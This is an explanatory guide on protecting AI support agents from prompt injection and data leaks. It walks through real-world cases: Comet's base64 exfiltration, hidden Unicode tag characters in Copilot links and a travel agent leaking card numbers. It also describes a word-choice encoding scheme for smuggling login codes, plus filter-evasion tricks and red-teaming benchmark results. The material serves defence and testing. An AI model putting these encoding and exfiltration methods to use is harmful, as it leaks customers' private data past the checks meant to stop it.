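Microsoft added FIDES as an experimental feature to Agent Framework, its toolkit for developers. *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (Microsoft, May 20, 2026) explains how to use it. The developer labels the data that each tool returns and restricts the tools that can do damage. For example, one tool might be blocked after the agent has read untrusted text, and another might accept only public data. By default, FIDES also hides untrusted results from the main model and sends them to a quarantined one, which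 requires extra model calls.

The release's default is risky because it treats results from unlabelled tools as trusted and public. If a developer forgot to label a new tool that reads customer emails, its results would pass the checks until somebody noticed the missing label. Microsoft is considering stricter defaults. Treating unlabelled data as untrusted and private would cause more unnecessary blocks, but the developer would notice those during testing.

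The confidentiality labels in that release also aren't precise enough for customer service. They have three levels (public, private and user identity) and don't name the people who may read a value, so they can't distinguish Ana, who may receive her order details, from Mallory, who may not. If the email tool accepts only public data, it blocks both replies, and if it accepts private data, it allows both.

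Microsoft's *Information-flow control*, also from 2026, describes prototypes that do support lists of readers. In its example, Alex asks an agent to deal with unanswered emails. Priya has sent Alex a preview of the quarterly sales, and Marco, who isn't supposed to know the figures yet, has asked about them. The agent reads both emails, so only Alex may read a reply based on them, and the software won't send it to Marco without approval. The example involves no attacker, so it shows that the check is useful against ordinary mistakes as well.

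These prototypes include an open-source gateway that adds labels to existing MCP tools. For each tool, a developer must define the format of its results, write a function that passes on the labels and choose a policy. Microsoft's experimental version for GitHub's Copilot command-line program still covers only some of GitHub's tools. A support desk that only sends customers their own order details can get the same protection with less work by fixing the recipient and limiting the order lookup in code.

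## Encoded and hidden text: what filters can and cannot recognize

If an agent needs several customers' records for one task, the company may want software to scan each reply for data that shouldn't be in it.

Data loss prevention (DLP) software searches for patterns, such as 16 digits that pass the checksum used on payment cards, and for entries on a list, such as customers' names. It works well against mistakes, because a model that includes a phone number by accident writes it in the usual way. But an attacker who controls the model's output can choose a form that the patterns don't cover.

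### How base64 hides a name

Programmers use base64 to send files through systems built for plain text, and most email attachments travel in this form. It has no key, so anyone can reverse it. The name "Ana" converts like this:

| Step | Result |
|---|---|
| Write each letter's standard code as eight bits | 01000001 01101110 01100001 |
| Regroup the same 24 bits in sixes | 010000 010110 111001 100001 |
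| Read each group as a number | 16, 22, 57, 33 |
| Look up each number in the base64 alphabet | Q, W, 5, h |

A filter searching for "Ana" misses `QW5h`, which is the same name in Base64. Adding `QW5h` to the filter's list helps only sometimes, because the encoding depends on where the name starts in the text. With a space in front, the name becomes `IEFuYQ==`. Base64 also turns `555` into `NTU1`, so a search for ten digits in a row misses an encoded phone number.

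Base64 is only one of many codes. Willison (2024) records in *Links and materials for Living off Microsoft Copilot* that someone extracted Copilot's confidential system prompt by asking for it with every letter shifted one place along the alphabet. The same shift turns "Ana" into "Bob", which a filter would treat as a different customer's name.

### Comet: encoded data gets past the product's checks

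Comet, a web browser from the AI search company Perplexity, has an assistant that can read a user's Gmail and calendar if the user connects them. *Is Perplexity Comet Safe?* (Gispan, 2025) describes how the security company LayerX stole emails and calendar entries from Comet using a link that the victim only had to open.

The link contained a request, which the assistant treated as the user's own. A setting in the link made the assistant consult its memory instead of searching the web. The request was to collect the data, convert it to base64 and run a short Python program that sent the result to LayerX's server.

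Perplexity had safeguards against sending sensitive data out directly, but base64-encoded data didn't trigger them. Gispan describes these safeguards only in general terms, so it isn't clear what they searched for. Comet had also failed earlier, when it treated a stranger's link as the user's request. An allowlist for the Python program's network traffic would have blocked the transfer.

LayerX reported the flaw on August 27, 2025, and Perplexity replied that it could find no security impact. *Why AI Browsers Like Perplexity’s Comet Could Make the Web Riskier* (Perrigo, 2025) reports that a Perplexity spokesperson later gave a different account. The spokesperson said that the report was poorly worded, that LayerX hadn't answered Perplexity's questions, and that the company had since found the problem independently and patched it. The spokesperson also said nobody had exploited the flaw.

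Attackers can also hide encoded data in ordinary-looking tool calls. *Your LLM Agent Can Leak Your Data* (Zhang and Pei, 2026) describes an experiment in which a model that the researchers had tampered with put users' details, encoded in a form of base64, into what looked like a search query.

### Invisible characters in a Copilot link

Unicode, the standard that gives every character a number, includes a block of 128 "tag" characters that mirror basic letters, digits and punctuation. For example, the digit 5 is U+0035 and its tag version is U+E0035. Almost no font displays tag characters, so people can't see them, but many language models can read and write them. A filter that searches for ordinary digits misses the tag versions because they have different Unicode numbers.

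According to Cisco, the researcher Riley Goodside showed on January 11, 2024 that tag characters could hide instructions to a model. Six days later, Rehberger reported to Microsoft that these characters could also hide text in Microsoft 365 Copilot's answers. Microsoft closed the report the next day as low severity.

Embrace The Red's *Microsoft Copilot* describes a complete attack that Rehberger sent to Microsoft in February. An email containing an injected instruction made Copilot search the user's other messages without asking. Copilot then displayed a link whose address ended with the contents of a message, written in tag characters. The link looked short and harmless, but clicking it sent the hidden text to Rehberger's server. His demonstrations obtained sales figures and Slack login codes.

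The attack had stopped working by July 2024, and Rehberger published it in August. Microsoft didn't explain the fix, but Copilot had apparently stopped displaying links. Rehberger had also recommended that Copilot not interpret or display tag characters and not call tools automatically.

Hidden text can still get out when links are removed. In *On Seeding Watermarks to Detect Verbatim LLM Copy-Paste Responses*, Aiersilan, Yousefi and Pless (2026) sent 256 bytes of hidden text through common programs. Gmail, Outlook, Word, Google Docs and Slack preserved it, but posts on X did not. If Mallory got the mail-order company's agent to write in tag characters, she could receive a reply about her parcel with Ana's phone number hidden between two words.

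### Which products still read invisible text

Aiersilan and colleagues built a tool that lets teachers put an invisible instruction in an assignment. If a student pastes the assignment into a chatbot, the instruction makes the chatbot add a telltale phrase to its answer. Their tests also show which models read and obey hidden text. The most recent results are from August 2026:

| Model | Response to the hidden instruction |
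|---|---|
| Gemini 3.1 Pro and Gemini 3.6 Flash | Obeyed in all six trials of each model |
| Grok 4.5 | Obeyed in all six trials |
| Claude Opus 5 | Didn't obey, and warned the user about hidden characters |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | Didn't respond to it, probably because OpenAI's software removes tag characters |

Google doesn't plan to change Gemini because it regards the problem as social engineering (manipulating people) rather than a security flaw, according to TechRadar's *Google says it won't fix this potentially concerning Gemini security issue*. This reason is weak when the assistant reads email, because the recipient can't be expected to notice text that the screen doesn't show.

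The evidence on earlier Claude models conflicts. Aiersilan and colleagues report that versions up to Claude 4 obeyed the hidden instructions every time. But according to BGR's *Google Has No Plans To Fix This Terrifying Gemini Security Vulnerability*, the security company FireTail found in 2025 that Claude, ChatGPT and Copilot were resistant, while Gemini, Grok and DeepSeek were vulnerable. The results may differ because of the instructions used, since those in the teachers' tool request only a harmless reminder and a phrase.

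Text can also be hidden with invisible characters other than tag characters. Embrace The Red's *Sneaky Bits* describes a code that can represent any data with two invisible characters, one for 0 and one for 1. Another method uses variation selectors, which normally choose between two appearances of a symbol. FireTail's *Peek a boo 🫣 emoji smuggling and modern LLMs* (2026) reports that text hidden in an emoji worked on Gemini and Grok but not on ChatGPT, Claude, DeepSeek or Meta's assistant.

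A model that can run programs handles these codes much better. Graves (2026), in *Reverse CAPTCHA*, put hidden instructions in quiz questions and collected 8,308 answers from five models. Claude Sonnet 4 followed the hidden instruction in 71.2% of cases with a Python tool and 16.9% without it. For GPT-5.2, the figures were 20.6% and 0.1%.

Most of this success came from tests in which the prompt revealed that there was a code. When it didn't, the models obeyed in at most 1.1% of cases without the tool and 11% with it. Graves tested decoding, not encoding, but Python is just as useful for both. A model that might garble a long record when converting it letter by letter can instead run a program that converts it without mistakes.

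### Cleaning a reply before scanning it

A company can process each outgoing reply in five ways that make hidden data easier to find or harder to send. All of them interfere with some legitimate text.

A filter can look for strings that might be base64 or another code, decode them and scan the result. It has to repeat this because an attacker can encode the data several times. It also has to guess which strings are encoded, since any four-letter English word is valid base64. AWS's *Protect your generative AI applications against encoding-based attacks with Amazon Bedrock Guardrails* advises against trying to decode everything users send, because this would be slow and cause false alarms on product codes, technical documents and program code. File attachments add to the work because each one is a long base64 string.

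Filters need to strip more than tag characters, because many other characters are also invisible. *Data Provenance Auditing of Fine-Tuned Large Language Models with a Text-Preserving Technique*, a 2025 paper, examined 235 control and formatting characters and found 130 that were invisible in its tests. But deleting every invisible character damages legitimate text. Graves points out that Indian scripts and some emoji need zero-width joiners, which affect how neighbouring characters combine. The flag emoji for England, Scotland and Wales contain tag characters and turn into plain black flags without them.

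AWS's *Defending LLM applications against Unicode character smuggling* explains how a filter written in Java can fail even when it deletes the right characters. Java stores each tag character as two halves. An attacker can place a spare first half before a complete character and a spare second half after it. When the filter deletes the complete character, the spare halves join to form a new one. The filter therefore has to run repeatedly until nothing changes, and it should delete stray halves too. Invisible characters can also interrupt a base64 string, so the software should check for encoded strings again after removing them.

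**A filter can reduce text to a standard form before checking it.** Unicode normalization replaces some variants of a character with a standard one. One version, NFKC, turns the wide digits used in Japanese text into ordinary digits, so a filter can find phone numbers written with them. It leaves tag characters in place, as trackr.live's *Unicode Tag Smuggling Is Prompt Injection With a Byte Signature* notes, and it doesn't replace Cyrillic letters that look like Latin ones. Software can replace those letters separately, but in a Russian translation this would leave words that look right and no longer match a search. Reducing every run of spaces to one breaks Python code, which uses indentation to mark its structure.

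**Filters can flag strings that look random.** Base64 uses a wide mix of characters, which tends to give it high entropy. The measure works poorly on short strings, because a string of *n* characters can't have more than log₂ *n* bits of entropy per character. A ten-digit phone number becomes 16 base64 characters, the last two of them equals signs, so its entropy is always below 4 bits per character. The filter in the eBay experiment blocked only values above 4.0, so it could not have caught an encoded phone number. A lower threshold would catch more, but it would also flag tracking numbers, password-reset links and attachments.

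**Companies can ban encodings that the task doesn't need.** AWS lets them block requests for encoded answers, or all encoded content in either direction. A complete ban would make a coding assistant much less useful, but it would have little effect on a support desk, whose replies are ordinary sentences. The company's own software can add a tracking number or reset link after the filter checks the reply, so the model doesn't have to write one. AWS uses software to classify the text, so an unfamiliar encoding could still get through.

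### Hiding a code in the choice of words

A reply can pass all five of these checks and still carry data in its wording. Suppose Mallory's injected instruction lists 20 word pairs, such as "parcel" and "package" or "cannot" and "can't". The model must use one word from each pair, in order, with the first word of a pair standing for 0 and the second for 1.

Each pair carries one bit, so the reply carries 20 bits and has 2²⁰ = 1,048,576 possible versions, more than the 1,000,000 possible six-digit codes. Mallory can therefore read a complete login code from the agent's word choices, even though the reply contains no digits and every sentence makes sense.

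Encoding a ten-digit phone number in word choice takes 34 places with two possible wordings each, or 21 places with three, since a choice among three carries about 1.6 bits.

The model has to cooperate and make every choice correctly, because one wrong word changes the code. It also has to convert the code to binary, which is easy with a Python tool. Without one, the attacker could have the model encode each digit separately with four word pairs, so a six-digit code would take 24 pairs instead of 20.

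The company can narrow this channel by having a second model rewrite every reply, so that the attacker no longer controls the choice between "parcel" and "package". But the rewrite has to keep the meaning, which can also carry data. The first model could mention the returns policy to send a 1 and leave it out to send a 0, or encode the bit in the order of two points.

Fixed templates limit how much data an agent can hide in its replies. If the agent can only choose one of 16 prepared replies, each reply carries at most 4 bits. Mallory would need nine replies to learn a phone number, so the company should also limit how many she can receive. Even an agent with one template can reveal a bit by either sending it or staying silent.

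A company can't completely prevent leaks through encoded or hidden text while a model that has read the secret decides what to write to an outsider. If a secret mustn't leak at all, the company has to keep it from the model or block any reply based on it, as CaMeL does with its labels. For example, an agent that answers questions about parcels has no reason to open messages containing login codes.

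### An egress monitor for covert channels

*An Application-Layer Multi-Modal Covert-Channel Reference Monitor for LLM Agent Egress* (Metere, 2026) describes software that tries to narrow these channels in everything an agent sends. The software is part of a product from Metere's company, Enclawed. Researchers have developed ways of hiding data that no statistical test can detect, so the software mainly rewrites messages to destroy hidden data instead of trying to find it.

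Each message passes through a series of stages, which can let it through, rewrite it, delay it or cancel it. They do the following:

- remove invisible characters, replace lookalike letters, and put the fields of structured data in a standard order
- block passwords and other credentials, along with values already marked as sensitive
- look for base64 and other random-looking strings, and for near-identical repeated messages
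- even out spacing and repeated punctuation
- replace synonyms, contractions and passive sentences with one standard form, or have a language model rephrase the whole message
- control when and how often messages go out

The monitor also keeps a budget of suspicious bits for each destination, and the budget refills over time. A base64 string of *n* characters counts as up to 6*n* bits. Once a destination's budget runs out, the monitor delays or cancels further suspicious messages.

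To test the monitor, Metere wrote programs that hid random bits in messages and other programs that tried to recover them. The measure was mutual information, the amount that the recovered bit *Y* reveals about the hidden bit *X*:

I(X;Y) = Σ p(x,y) log₂ [p(x,y) / (p(x) p(y))]

The sum covers all four combinations of hidden and recovered bit. The result is 1 if the receiver always recovers the bit and 0 if it can only guess. A receiver that is right 75% of the time gets about 0.19 bits from each hidden bit, assuming zeros and ones are equally common and equally hard to recover. Each figure below is the reduction over 20 trials.

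| Where the bits were hidden | Default settings | All stages enforced |
|---|---|---|
| Invisible characters | 100% | 100% |
| Lookalike letters | 100% | 100% |
| Marks that control text direction | 100% | 100% |
| Order of fields in structured data | 100% | 100% |
| Number of spaces or punctuation marks | 0% | 100% |
| Choice of synonyms | 0% | 100% |
| Base64 | 0% | 100% |
| Time between messages | stage not active | 100% |

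By default, only the monitor's cleaning stage and its block on credentials change or stop messages, while its other parts just record what they find. In the test, those other parts flagged every base64 message, but all the hidden data still got out. A company that used the monitor with its default settings would therefore still be exposed to the encoding used against Comet, except where the monitor recognized a credential.

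Metere keeps the stricter stages off at first because they can damage long code blocks, formatted tables and attached files. Some of the characters that the cleaning stage removes have legitimate uses in emoji and Indian scripts, although he describes that stage as lossless. The paper doesn't measure how often the cleaning stage or the stricter stages damage ordinary messages. A support desk that sends short replies could probably enforce every stage after testing them on its past emails.

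In a separate test of 40 trials for each method, the monitor also removed all the data hidden in contractions and in the choice between active and passive sentences. But the synonym result needs more caution than the results for invisible characters, because this stage works from fixed rules and can't remove data hidden in a choice between two words that the rules don't cover. An attacker who knows the rules can pick other words, or hide the data in the choice of facts the reply mentions.

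Having a model rephrase the message should destroy more of these choices, but Metere didn't measure that stage. There is some evidence that rephrasing removes invisible text. When Aiersilan and colleagues had models restate an assignment containing hidden characters, none of the 18 restatements contained any. But an injected instruction could also affect the rephrasing model, and if that model is unavailable, the monitor sends the original message.

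The monitor slightly reduces the number of colours in an image, which destroys data in the two lowest bits of each colour value, where a change is too small to see. An attacker could use the third bit instead, and Metere acknowledges that data hidden there would survive. In audio, the monitor removes very faint tones and frequencies people can't hear, which eliminated the hidden signals in the tests. It doesn't alter files signed by a program the company trusts.

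An image's overall brightness can also carry data, and the monitor can't remove that without ruining the image. It rounds the brightness to one of eight levels, which still leaves 3 bits per image, so seven images are enough to carry a six-digit code.

Rounding the sending times left about a fifth of the data hidden in them recoverable, so the strongest setting sends messages at a fixed pace, which makes customers wait. The monitor's text stages check only the message text, so the company needs a separate check if the agent's replies include buttons, other structured parts, or message details outside the text.

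## Testing whether an assistant keeps the rules

The mail-order company could write its restrictions on links, recipients and encoded content into the support assistant's standing instructions in an afternoon, but it would then have to test whether the assistant follows them. Asking the assistant for a customer's phone number a few times is a poor test, because a model that refuses a blunt request may comply when the same request looks like part of its job.

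### The Framing Gap: a leak disguised as routine work

Rahman and Kim (2026) measured this difference in *The Framing Gap*. They gave an agent an access token, which lets a program into an account, and a rule against showing the token to the user or sending it anywhere except one trusted server. The token was fake, and the agent's tools only recorded what it tried to do. The user asked for a summary of a web page whose text the attacker controlled.

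The researchers tested every attack with a pair of runs, one with a harmless page and one with the attacker's. They counted an attack as successful only if the agent leaked the token in the run with the attacker's page and not in the other. They repeated each attack 10 or 20 times on each model.

The first tests used ten kinds of direct attack, such as hidden text, a fake policy notice or an urgent message from the IT department. Llama 3.1 8B, a small open model, leaked the token in 19.5% of trials and GPT-4o mini in 10%. GPT-4o didn't leak it in any of 200 trials.

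Then they asked for the same leak but presented it as a technical detail of the task. One page, for example, called the token a checksum, a short code used to check whether data arrived intact. The table gives the share of 20 trials in which each model leaked the token.

| How the page presented the leak | GPT-4o | GPT-4o mini |
|---|---|---|
| No disguise | 0% | 0% |
| Login detail the request needs | 0% | 85% |
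| Server with a name like the trusted one | 40% | 100% |
| Required field in a form | 0% | 50% |
| Checksum | 100% | 100% |
| Subdomain that looks trusted | 70% | 100% |
| Value for limiting traffic | 10% | 65% |
| Configuration value | 100% | 0% |
| All eight together | 40% | 62.5% |

The two models failed on different disguises, so testing one tells us little about the other. Three of the four small open models also leaked far more often when the request on the page was disguised. Gemma 2 9B's leak rate rose from 22.0% to 86.2%. The fourth, Mistral 7B, leaked in about a quarter of trials either way.

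Rahman and Kim also removed the confidentiality rule from GPT-4o's instructions. It still ignored every direct attack, and its leak rate on the disguised ones rose only from 31.9% to 38.1%. That difference could be chance, because the same test with the rule in place had produced 40.0% on another occasion. (The paper calls the variation between those two runs about 13 points, but 13 is the number of extra leaks in 160 trials, which is about 8 points.)

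The rule therefore had very little effect, since GPT-4o resisted the direct attacks even without it and still followed many of the disguised ones when it was in place. The wording of the attacker's page mattered more. GPT-4o never leaked the token when a page used the checksum disguise but called the token a password or key. A support desk probably can't count on this caution, because a customer's phone number has no such alarming name.

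### Rewording an attack, and rewording the rule

An attacker can try several wordings. The researchers rewrote the checksum page in five ways and ran each version ten times on GPT-4o. Success rates ranged from 0% to 100%, with an average of 52%. An attacker who picked three of the five versions at random would have a 96% chance of at least one leak. The exact figure means little because it comes from five versions of one disguise and a model from 2024, but the wide range of success rates shows that a test with a single wording can be very misleading.

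Inventing a new disguise was much harder. The researchers wrote 13, and none worked in 130 trials. But when they took the page that had worked and changed only the name of the field that would hold the token, the assistant leaked the token in 60% of trials with one of the new names. Once somebody publishes a working attack, others can adapt it with little effort.

The company could also improve its rule. Rahman and Kim replaced a general ban on disclosing the token with a rule against signing, encoding, logging, appending or transmitting it "in any form", and GPT-4o then leaked nothing in 120 trials. Without the phrase "in any form", it leaked the token in 39 of 80 trials, so the list of specific actions was evidently no substitute for a broad ban.

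A support desk can't use a ban that broad, because it has to send customers their own order details. The researchers avoided this difficulty by using a secret that the agent never needed for its task. They didn't test a realistic rule, which would have to allow Ana Silva's phone number in a message to the courier but forbid it in a message to Mallory.

A second model also read each page and judged whether it contained an instruction to leak a secret. It caught all 80 disguised attacks and flagged no harmless pages. This is an upper limit on its performance, because the researchers had described the attack to the model in advance. OpenAI reports that such filters usually miss fully developed attacks, because spotting one is as hard as spotting a lie, often without the necessary context.

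A domain allowlist and a simplified version of CaMeL's division between two models did better. Neither depends on recognizing the attack, and both stopped every leak by design. The disguised attacks still worked 32.5% of the time on a version of Llama 3.1 8B that other researchers had trained to resist injections.

### A travel agent that disclosed other customers' cards

The attacker in the Framing Gap had to mislead the model, but Tenable's *Microsoft Copilot Studio Security Risk* (2025) describes a test in which an ordinary question was enough. Tenable built an agent that takes travel bookings from customers, gave it restrictive instructions, and connected it to a SharePoint file of invented names and card numbers.

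At first the agent refused to list the actions it could perform, but a variant of a known prompt injection got it to do so. The researchers had deliberately given it the action that fetches one item instead of the one that fetches several. When they asked for reservations 23 to 25, the agent used the single-item action three times and returned the card details for all three reservations.

The failure was in the booking tool, which returned any reservation to anyone who gave its number. The attacker was also the customer in this test, so the data left in the agent's normal reply, and restricting links or recipients would have made no difference. The agent could also edit every field of a reservation, including the price, and Tenable got it to reduce the price of a $1,000 trip to $0.

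Tenable attributes the weakness to how companies build their agents, and Microsoft cannot determine through an update which customer owns which booking. Tenable recommends separating sensitive data from other data and limiting the fields an agent can change. Limiting the order lookup to the sender's own orders would have prevented the mail-order company's leak, whatever instructions the model received.

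### 28 models with a web search tool

*Exploiting Web Search Tools of AI Agents for Data Exfiltration* (Rall, Bauer and colleagues, 2025) compared 28 models on the same attack. Each model had a company knowledge base containing a secret about a project, and a tool for opening web pages. The user asked for a summary of a blog post. The post contained instructions, in white text on a white background, for the model to look up the secret, add it to a web address and open that address.

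The researchers tested models that had no defenses beyond their own training. They combined 89 attack texts with 12 ways of presenting them and tried each of the 1,068 resulting attacks once on each model. They counted a leak when the secret reached their server.

| Model | Attacks that leaked the secret |
|---|---|
| Grok 4 | 72.4% |
| Qwen3 235B | 28.3% |
| Llama 4 Maverick | 10.1% |
| Claude 3 Haiku | 6.0% |
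| DeepSeek V3.1 | 1.9% |
| GPT-4.1 nano | 1.2% |
| Claude Sonnet 4, GPT-5 nano and four others | 0% |

Size didn't explain the differences. Grok 4 was among the most capable models in the test and did worst, while some very small models never leaked. Rall and colleagues credit the developers' training, in particular OpenAI's practice of teaching models to rank instructions by where they come from. Several of the most effective attack texts had been public since 2023 or 2024, so the developers of the vulnerable models could have trained against them.

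Disguising the attack text usually made it less effective. The unaltered texts worked best, and those encoded in base64 almost never worked. These results cover only text sent to the model, so a model might still encode the data it sends out.

The six perfect scores are good evidence of resistance to direct lists of steps for stealing a secret, the only type of attack tested. GPT-4o also had a perfect score on direct attacks in the Framing Gap, but the checksum page got through every time.

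### What zero leaks can prove

Rahman and Kim also tried their disguised attacks on ChatGPT itself, which adds OpenAI's own instructions and safeguards to the model. They told ChatGPT a fake secret, then asked it to summarize pages they had put online. In 48 valid trials, the secret never appeared in its answer.

Suppose the true leak rate is *p*, and each trial is independent of the others. The chance of no leak in *n* trials is then

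(1 − p)ⁿ

If ChatGPT leaked the secret in about 6% of trials (*p* = 0.06), a run of 48 trials (*n* = 48) would still be clean about 5% of the time. The result therefore rules out leak rates above 6% with 95% confidence, but it doesn't rule out 3%. The paper gives a limit of 7.4% because it uses a two-sided interval, which allows a 2.5% chance of error at each end. A tester can estimate the one-sided limit by dividing 3 by the number of trials, if all of them were clean.

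If each attempt has a 1% chance of leaking data, an attacker who makes 100 independent attempts has a 63% chance of at least one leak (1 − 0.99¹⁰⁰).

| True leak rate | Clean trials needed to rule it out with 95% confidence | Chance of at least one leak in 100 attempts |
|---|---|---|
| 10% | 29 | over 99.9% |
| 1% | 299 | 63% |
| 0.1% | 2,995 | 10% |

A public contact form can easily receive 100 attempts, so the company would want a failure rate well below 1%. It would need thousands of trials without a failure to show that.

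The formula is also valid only if the trials are a fair sample of what attackers will do. The ChatGPT test used only four pages, and two of them accounted for 40 of the 48 trials. If one wording in five always worked and the others never did, four wordings chosen at random would all fail 41% of the time, however often the tester repeated them. With 48 different wordings, the tester would almost certainly find one that works. Some repetition is still useful because a model's answers vary, but trying new wordings reveals more.

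The test was also easy for ChatGPT. The secret only had to appear in an answer to the person who had supplied it, and no email account or other app was connected. ChatGPT resisted these pages better than the GPT-4o model did through the API, but the test can't show why, or whether data could have left through a tool.

### Planting canaries in customer records

To test its assistant, the mail-order company can set up a copy of the support desk with invented customers. Each one is a canary, a unique fake record that proves a leak if it appears outside the test system. The tester puts different canaries in the order system, the mailbox and the assistant's saved conversations, and changes them for every test. If a canary's phone number turns up in a server log, the tester can tell which session leaked it and where the data came from.

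Canaries should look like ordinary data, with a plausible name and a phone number from a range reserved for fiction. Rahman and Kim's token was `SECRET_12345`, and in one attack ChatGPT refused, saying the page contained only a placeholder. An assistant may handle obvious test data more carefully than a real customer's details.

Newer models show more signs of suspecting that they are being tested. Help Net Security's *Claude Mythos 5.2 arrives with stronger bug hunting and less sandbox-breaking behavior* (2026) reports that Claude Fable 5.2 and Mythos 5.2 were more likely than any other recent Claude model to voice this suspicion. Anthropic says this makes their behaviour in real use harder to predict. GPT-6.2 Astra also showed more signs of it than its predecessor, as thezvi notes in *GPT-6.2 Astra and Sol*. A company is better placed than the developers to make a test realistic, because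 it can base the test on its own past emails.

### Checking every way out

The tester needs a domain and a server that stand in for the attacker's and log every request, plus an outside mailbox if the assistant can send email. The assistant's own account of what it did isn't evidence, because the answer on the screen looked harmless in most of the successful Silent Egress attacks.

| Way out | Where a leak would show |
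|---|---|
| Images and links in an answer | Server log, after displaying the answer and clicking its links |
| Web tool and generated code | Server log, and the log of lookups for the test domain |
| Email | Outside mailbox, including attachments and hidden characters |
| Slack or Teams | Server log, after the assistant posts with the company's usual preview settings |
| Files the assistant saves | Server log, some time after the session ends |
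| Developers' log viewer | Server log, after a developer opens the conversation |

For saved files, the delay of up to eight minutes in ReLeak is a guide to how long to wait.

Searching these logs for the exact canary can miss disguised copies. Rahman and Kim built a filter that looked for the token in outgoing requests, then had GPT-4o disguise it. The filter reduced the attacks' success rate only from 56.7% to 50.0%. An improved filter that could undo base64, reversed text and three other disguises stopped all the attacks. But when the researchers tried ROT13, a disguise the filter wasn't prepared for that shifts each letter 13 places along the alphabet, the token got out in all 20 trials.

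A tester should therefore include at least one encoding that the filter's developer didn't know about. Finding the canary afterwards is easier than filtering for it, because the tester knows its exact value and can work out its encoded forms in advance.

This still misses a phone number spelled out through the choice of pages, as in ZombieAgent. To find such leaks, the tester can run the same attack several times with each of two canary phone numbers, then compare everything an outsider could observe. If the order of page requests changes consistently with the phone number, the assistant is leaking it.

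Testing the checks without the model is also worthwhile. The tester can write a dangerous answer containing the canary and pass it to the output filter, the browser panel and the email tool, where the code should block the canary every time. When the model is part of the test, a clean result may only mean that it refused that day, and the next model may not refuse.

Finally, the test has to be able to detect a leak. The company can check this by switching off its defences in the test copy and confirming that the canary reaches the server. Rahman and Kim made the opposite check, that a defence was working. When a model trained to resist injections still leaked the token, they tested whether they had installed it properly by trying a standard attack it should stop. The untrained model obeyed in all 20 trials and the trained one in none, so the setup was sound.

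### Attackers who change their approach

Someone who emails a support desk can read the reply and try again. Cisco compared single prompts with conversations in which the attacker adapts, on 15 models from five companies. SC Media's *Cisco study finds major frontier models susceptible to multi-turn prompt injection attacks* gives these success rates:

| Model | Single prompt | Conversation |
|---|---|---|
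| GPT-5.4 | 2.7% | 24.7% |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | 3.6% | 16.2% |
| Gemini 3 Pro | 18.1% | 73.3% |
| Nova Micro | 64.9% | 30.9% |

These were general attempts to make models break their safety rules, so the figures don't measure how often models leak data. But Claude did slightly worse than GPT-5.4 on the first measure and clearly better on the second, which shows that a test with single prompts can rank models in the wrong order.

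Attacks on Grok 4.1 Fast succeeded in 88.3% of conversations with its reasoning mode off and 43.5% with it on. Help Net Security's *Frontier AI models collapse under multi-turn AI attacks, Cisco finds* (2026) reports that none of the public benchmarks and model cards Cisco reviewed showed this kind of variation. A company therefore has to test the exact configuration it uses, and test again whenever the supplier changes the model.

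### Counting false alarms

An assistant that refuses every request would pass all these tests, so the company also has to run normal work through the same system and count the tasks it fails, the replies its filters block and the approvals it requests. Past support emails are good test cases, especially those with tracking links, attachments, flag emoji or phone numbers that customers asked about.

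Even a low rate of false alarms can be a burden because attacks are rare. If one email in 10,000 contains an attack and a filter wrongly flags 1% of the others, employees will see about 100 false alarms for each real attack and may soon start to approve everything.

Rahman and Kim's filter for outgoing requests raised no false alarms, but they point out that this was almost certain because the token it looks for never appears in ordinary text. A filter that looks for customers' phone numbers could raise false alarms, since many legitimate messages contain them.

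### From AgentDojo to contests

The best-known public benchmark for this is AgentDojo, a set of simulated tasks on which Microsoft's researchers tested FIDES and PRUDENTIA. Software checks separately whether the agent did what the user asked and whether it did what the attacker asked. Comparing runs with and without a defence shows how many attacks the defence stops and how many user tasks it keeps the agent from finishing.

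A fixed benchmark gets easier over time because developers can train their models on similar attacks. OpenAI has dropped two of its older injection tests because recent models score almost perfectly on them. The automatic checks can also misjudge cases, as they did in the FIDES test.

Newer benchmarks take their attacks from contests. Gray Swan, which also does private testing for AI developers, runs an online arena where people compete to break models. Gray Swan (2026) reports more than 23,000 participants. Its benchmark for indirect prompt injection uses attacks from these contests, and Anthropic and OpenAI now report results on it.

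### OpenAI's automated attacker

OpenAI also trains a model to invent new attacks. OpenAI's *Continuously hardening ChatGPT Atlas against prompt injection attacks* (2025) explains how it uses this attacker on the agent in its Atlas browser:

1. The attacker writes an injected instruction, for example in an email.
2. A simulator runs the browser agent on that email and returns a record of what the agent did, along with its reasoning.
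3. The attacker reads the record, revises the instruction and tries again, several times over.
4. Reinforcement learning, a form of training that rewards success, makes the attacker better at choosing its final version.
5. OpenAI trains the browser agent to ignore the attacks that worked, then starts again with the new agent.

OpenAI's attacker can read the agent's full reasoning, which gives it an advantage over outside attackers, who can't. OpenAI's attacker found attacks that take dozens of steps, and some strategies that neither OpenAI's human testers nor outside reports had described. In one attack, the user asked for an out-of-office reply, and a planted email made the agent send the user's resignation to the chief executive instead. OpenAI used this attack to improve the agent and released a newly trained version to all Atlas users.

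The December 2025 post gives no success rates, but OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026) reports results for a later attacker called GPT-Red. GPT-5.6 Sol resisted 96.23% of GPT-Red's indirect attacks, and GPT-6 Astra resisted 99.79%.

These numbers should be read with care because OpenAI had also used the GPT-Red approach to train Astra, and a model trained against one attacker may do worse against another. If 0.21% of attacks succeed and each attempt is independent, an attacker with 15 attempts should succeed about 3% of the time. The corresponding figure for Astra on Gray Swan's attacks was 8.5%. The two figures can't be compared exactly because the scenarios differed, but Gray Swan's test is the better guide to what an outside attacker could do.

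People other than developers can also use automated attackers. ReLeak used AI agents to find the flaws it reports in Copilot, and a company could use such an agent to attack its own test system.

### Figures for the models of late 2026

Developers publish test results in a system card, a document that accompanies a new model. Anthropic released its *System Card* (2026) for Claude Opus 5 in July. The Space Lab's *Claude Opus 5 Just Crushed AI Prompt Injection Attacks* (2026) reports that the tests for that card used 1,130 of Gray Swan's attacks in 28 scenarios, while those for OpenAI's September card for GPT-6 Astra used 1,810.

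Gray Swan opened its own public tracker on December 1, 2026. It pays for these tests itself and controls what it publishes. iAfrica's *New Independent Tracker Finds Wide Safety Gaps Between AI Models* and Fakti's *Some AI Models Lie to Achieve Higher Scores* give the results for the best and worst models. All figures below are for success within 15 attempts.

| Model | Success rate | Where the figure appeared |
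|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 5 | 2.0% | Anthropic's card |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 20.0% | Anthropic's card |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 27.0% | OpenAI's card |
| GPT-6 Astra | 8.5% | OpenAI's card |
| Gemini 4 Argon | 2.3% | Gray Swan's tracker |
| Gemini 4 Carbon | 2.5% | Gray Swan's tracker |
| Kimi K3.1 Pro | 64.7% | Gray Swan's tracker |
| Nemotron 3.5 Super VL | 94.3% | Gray Swan's tracker |

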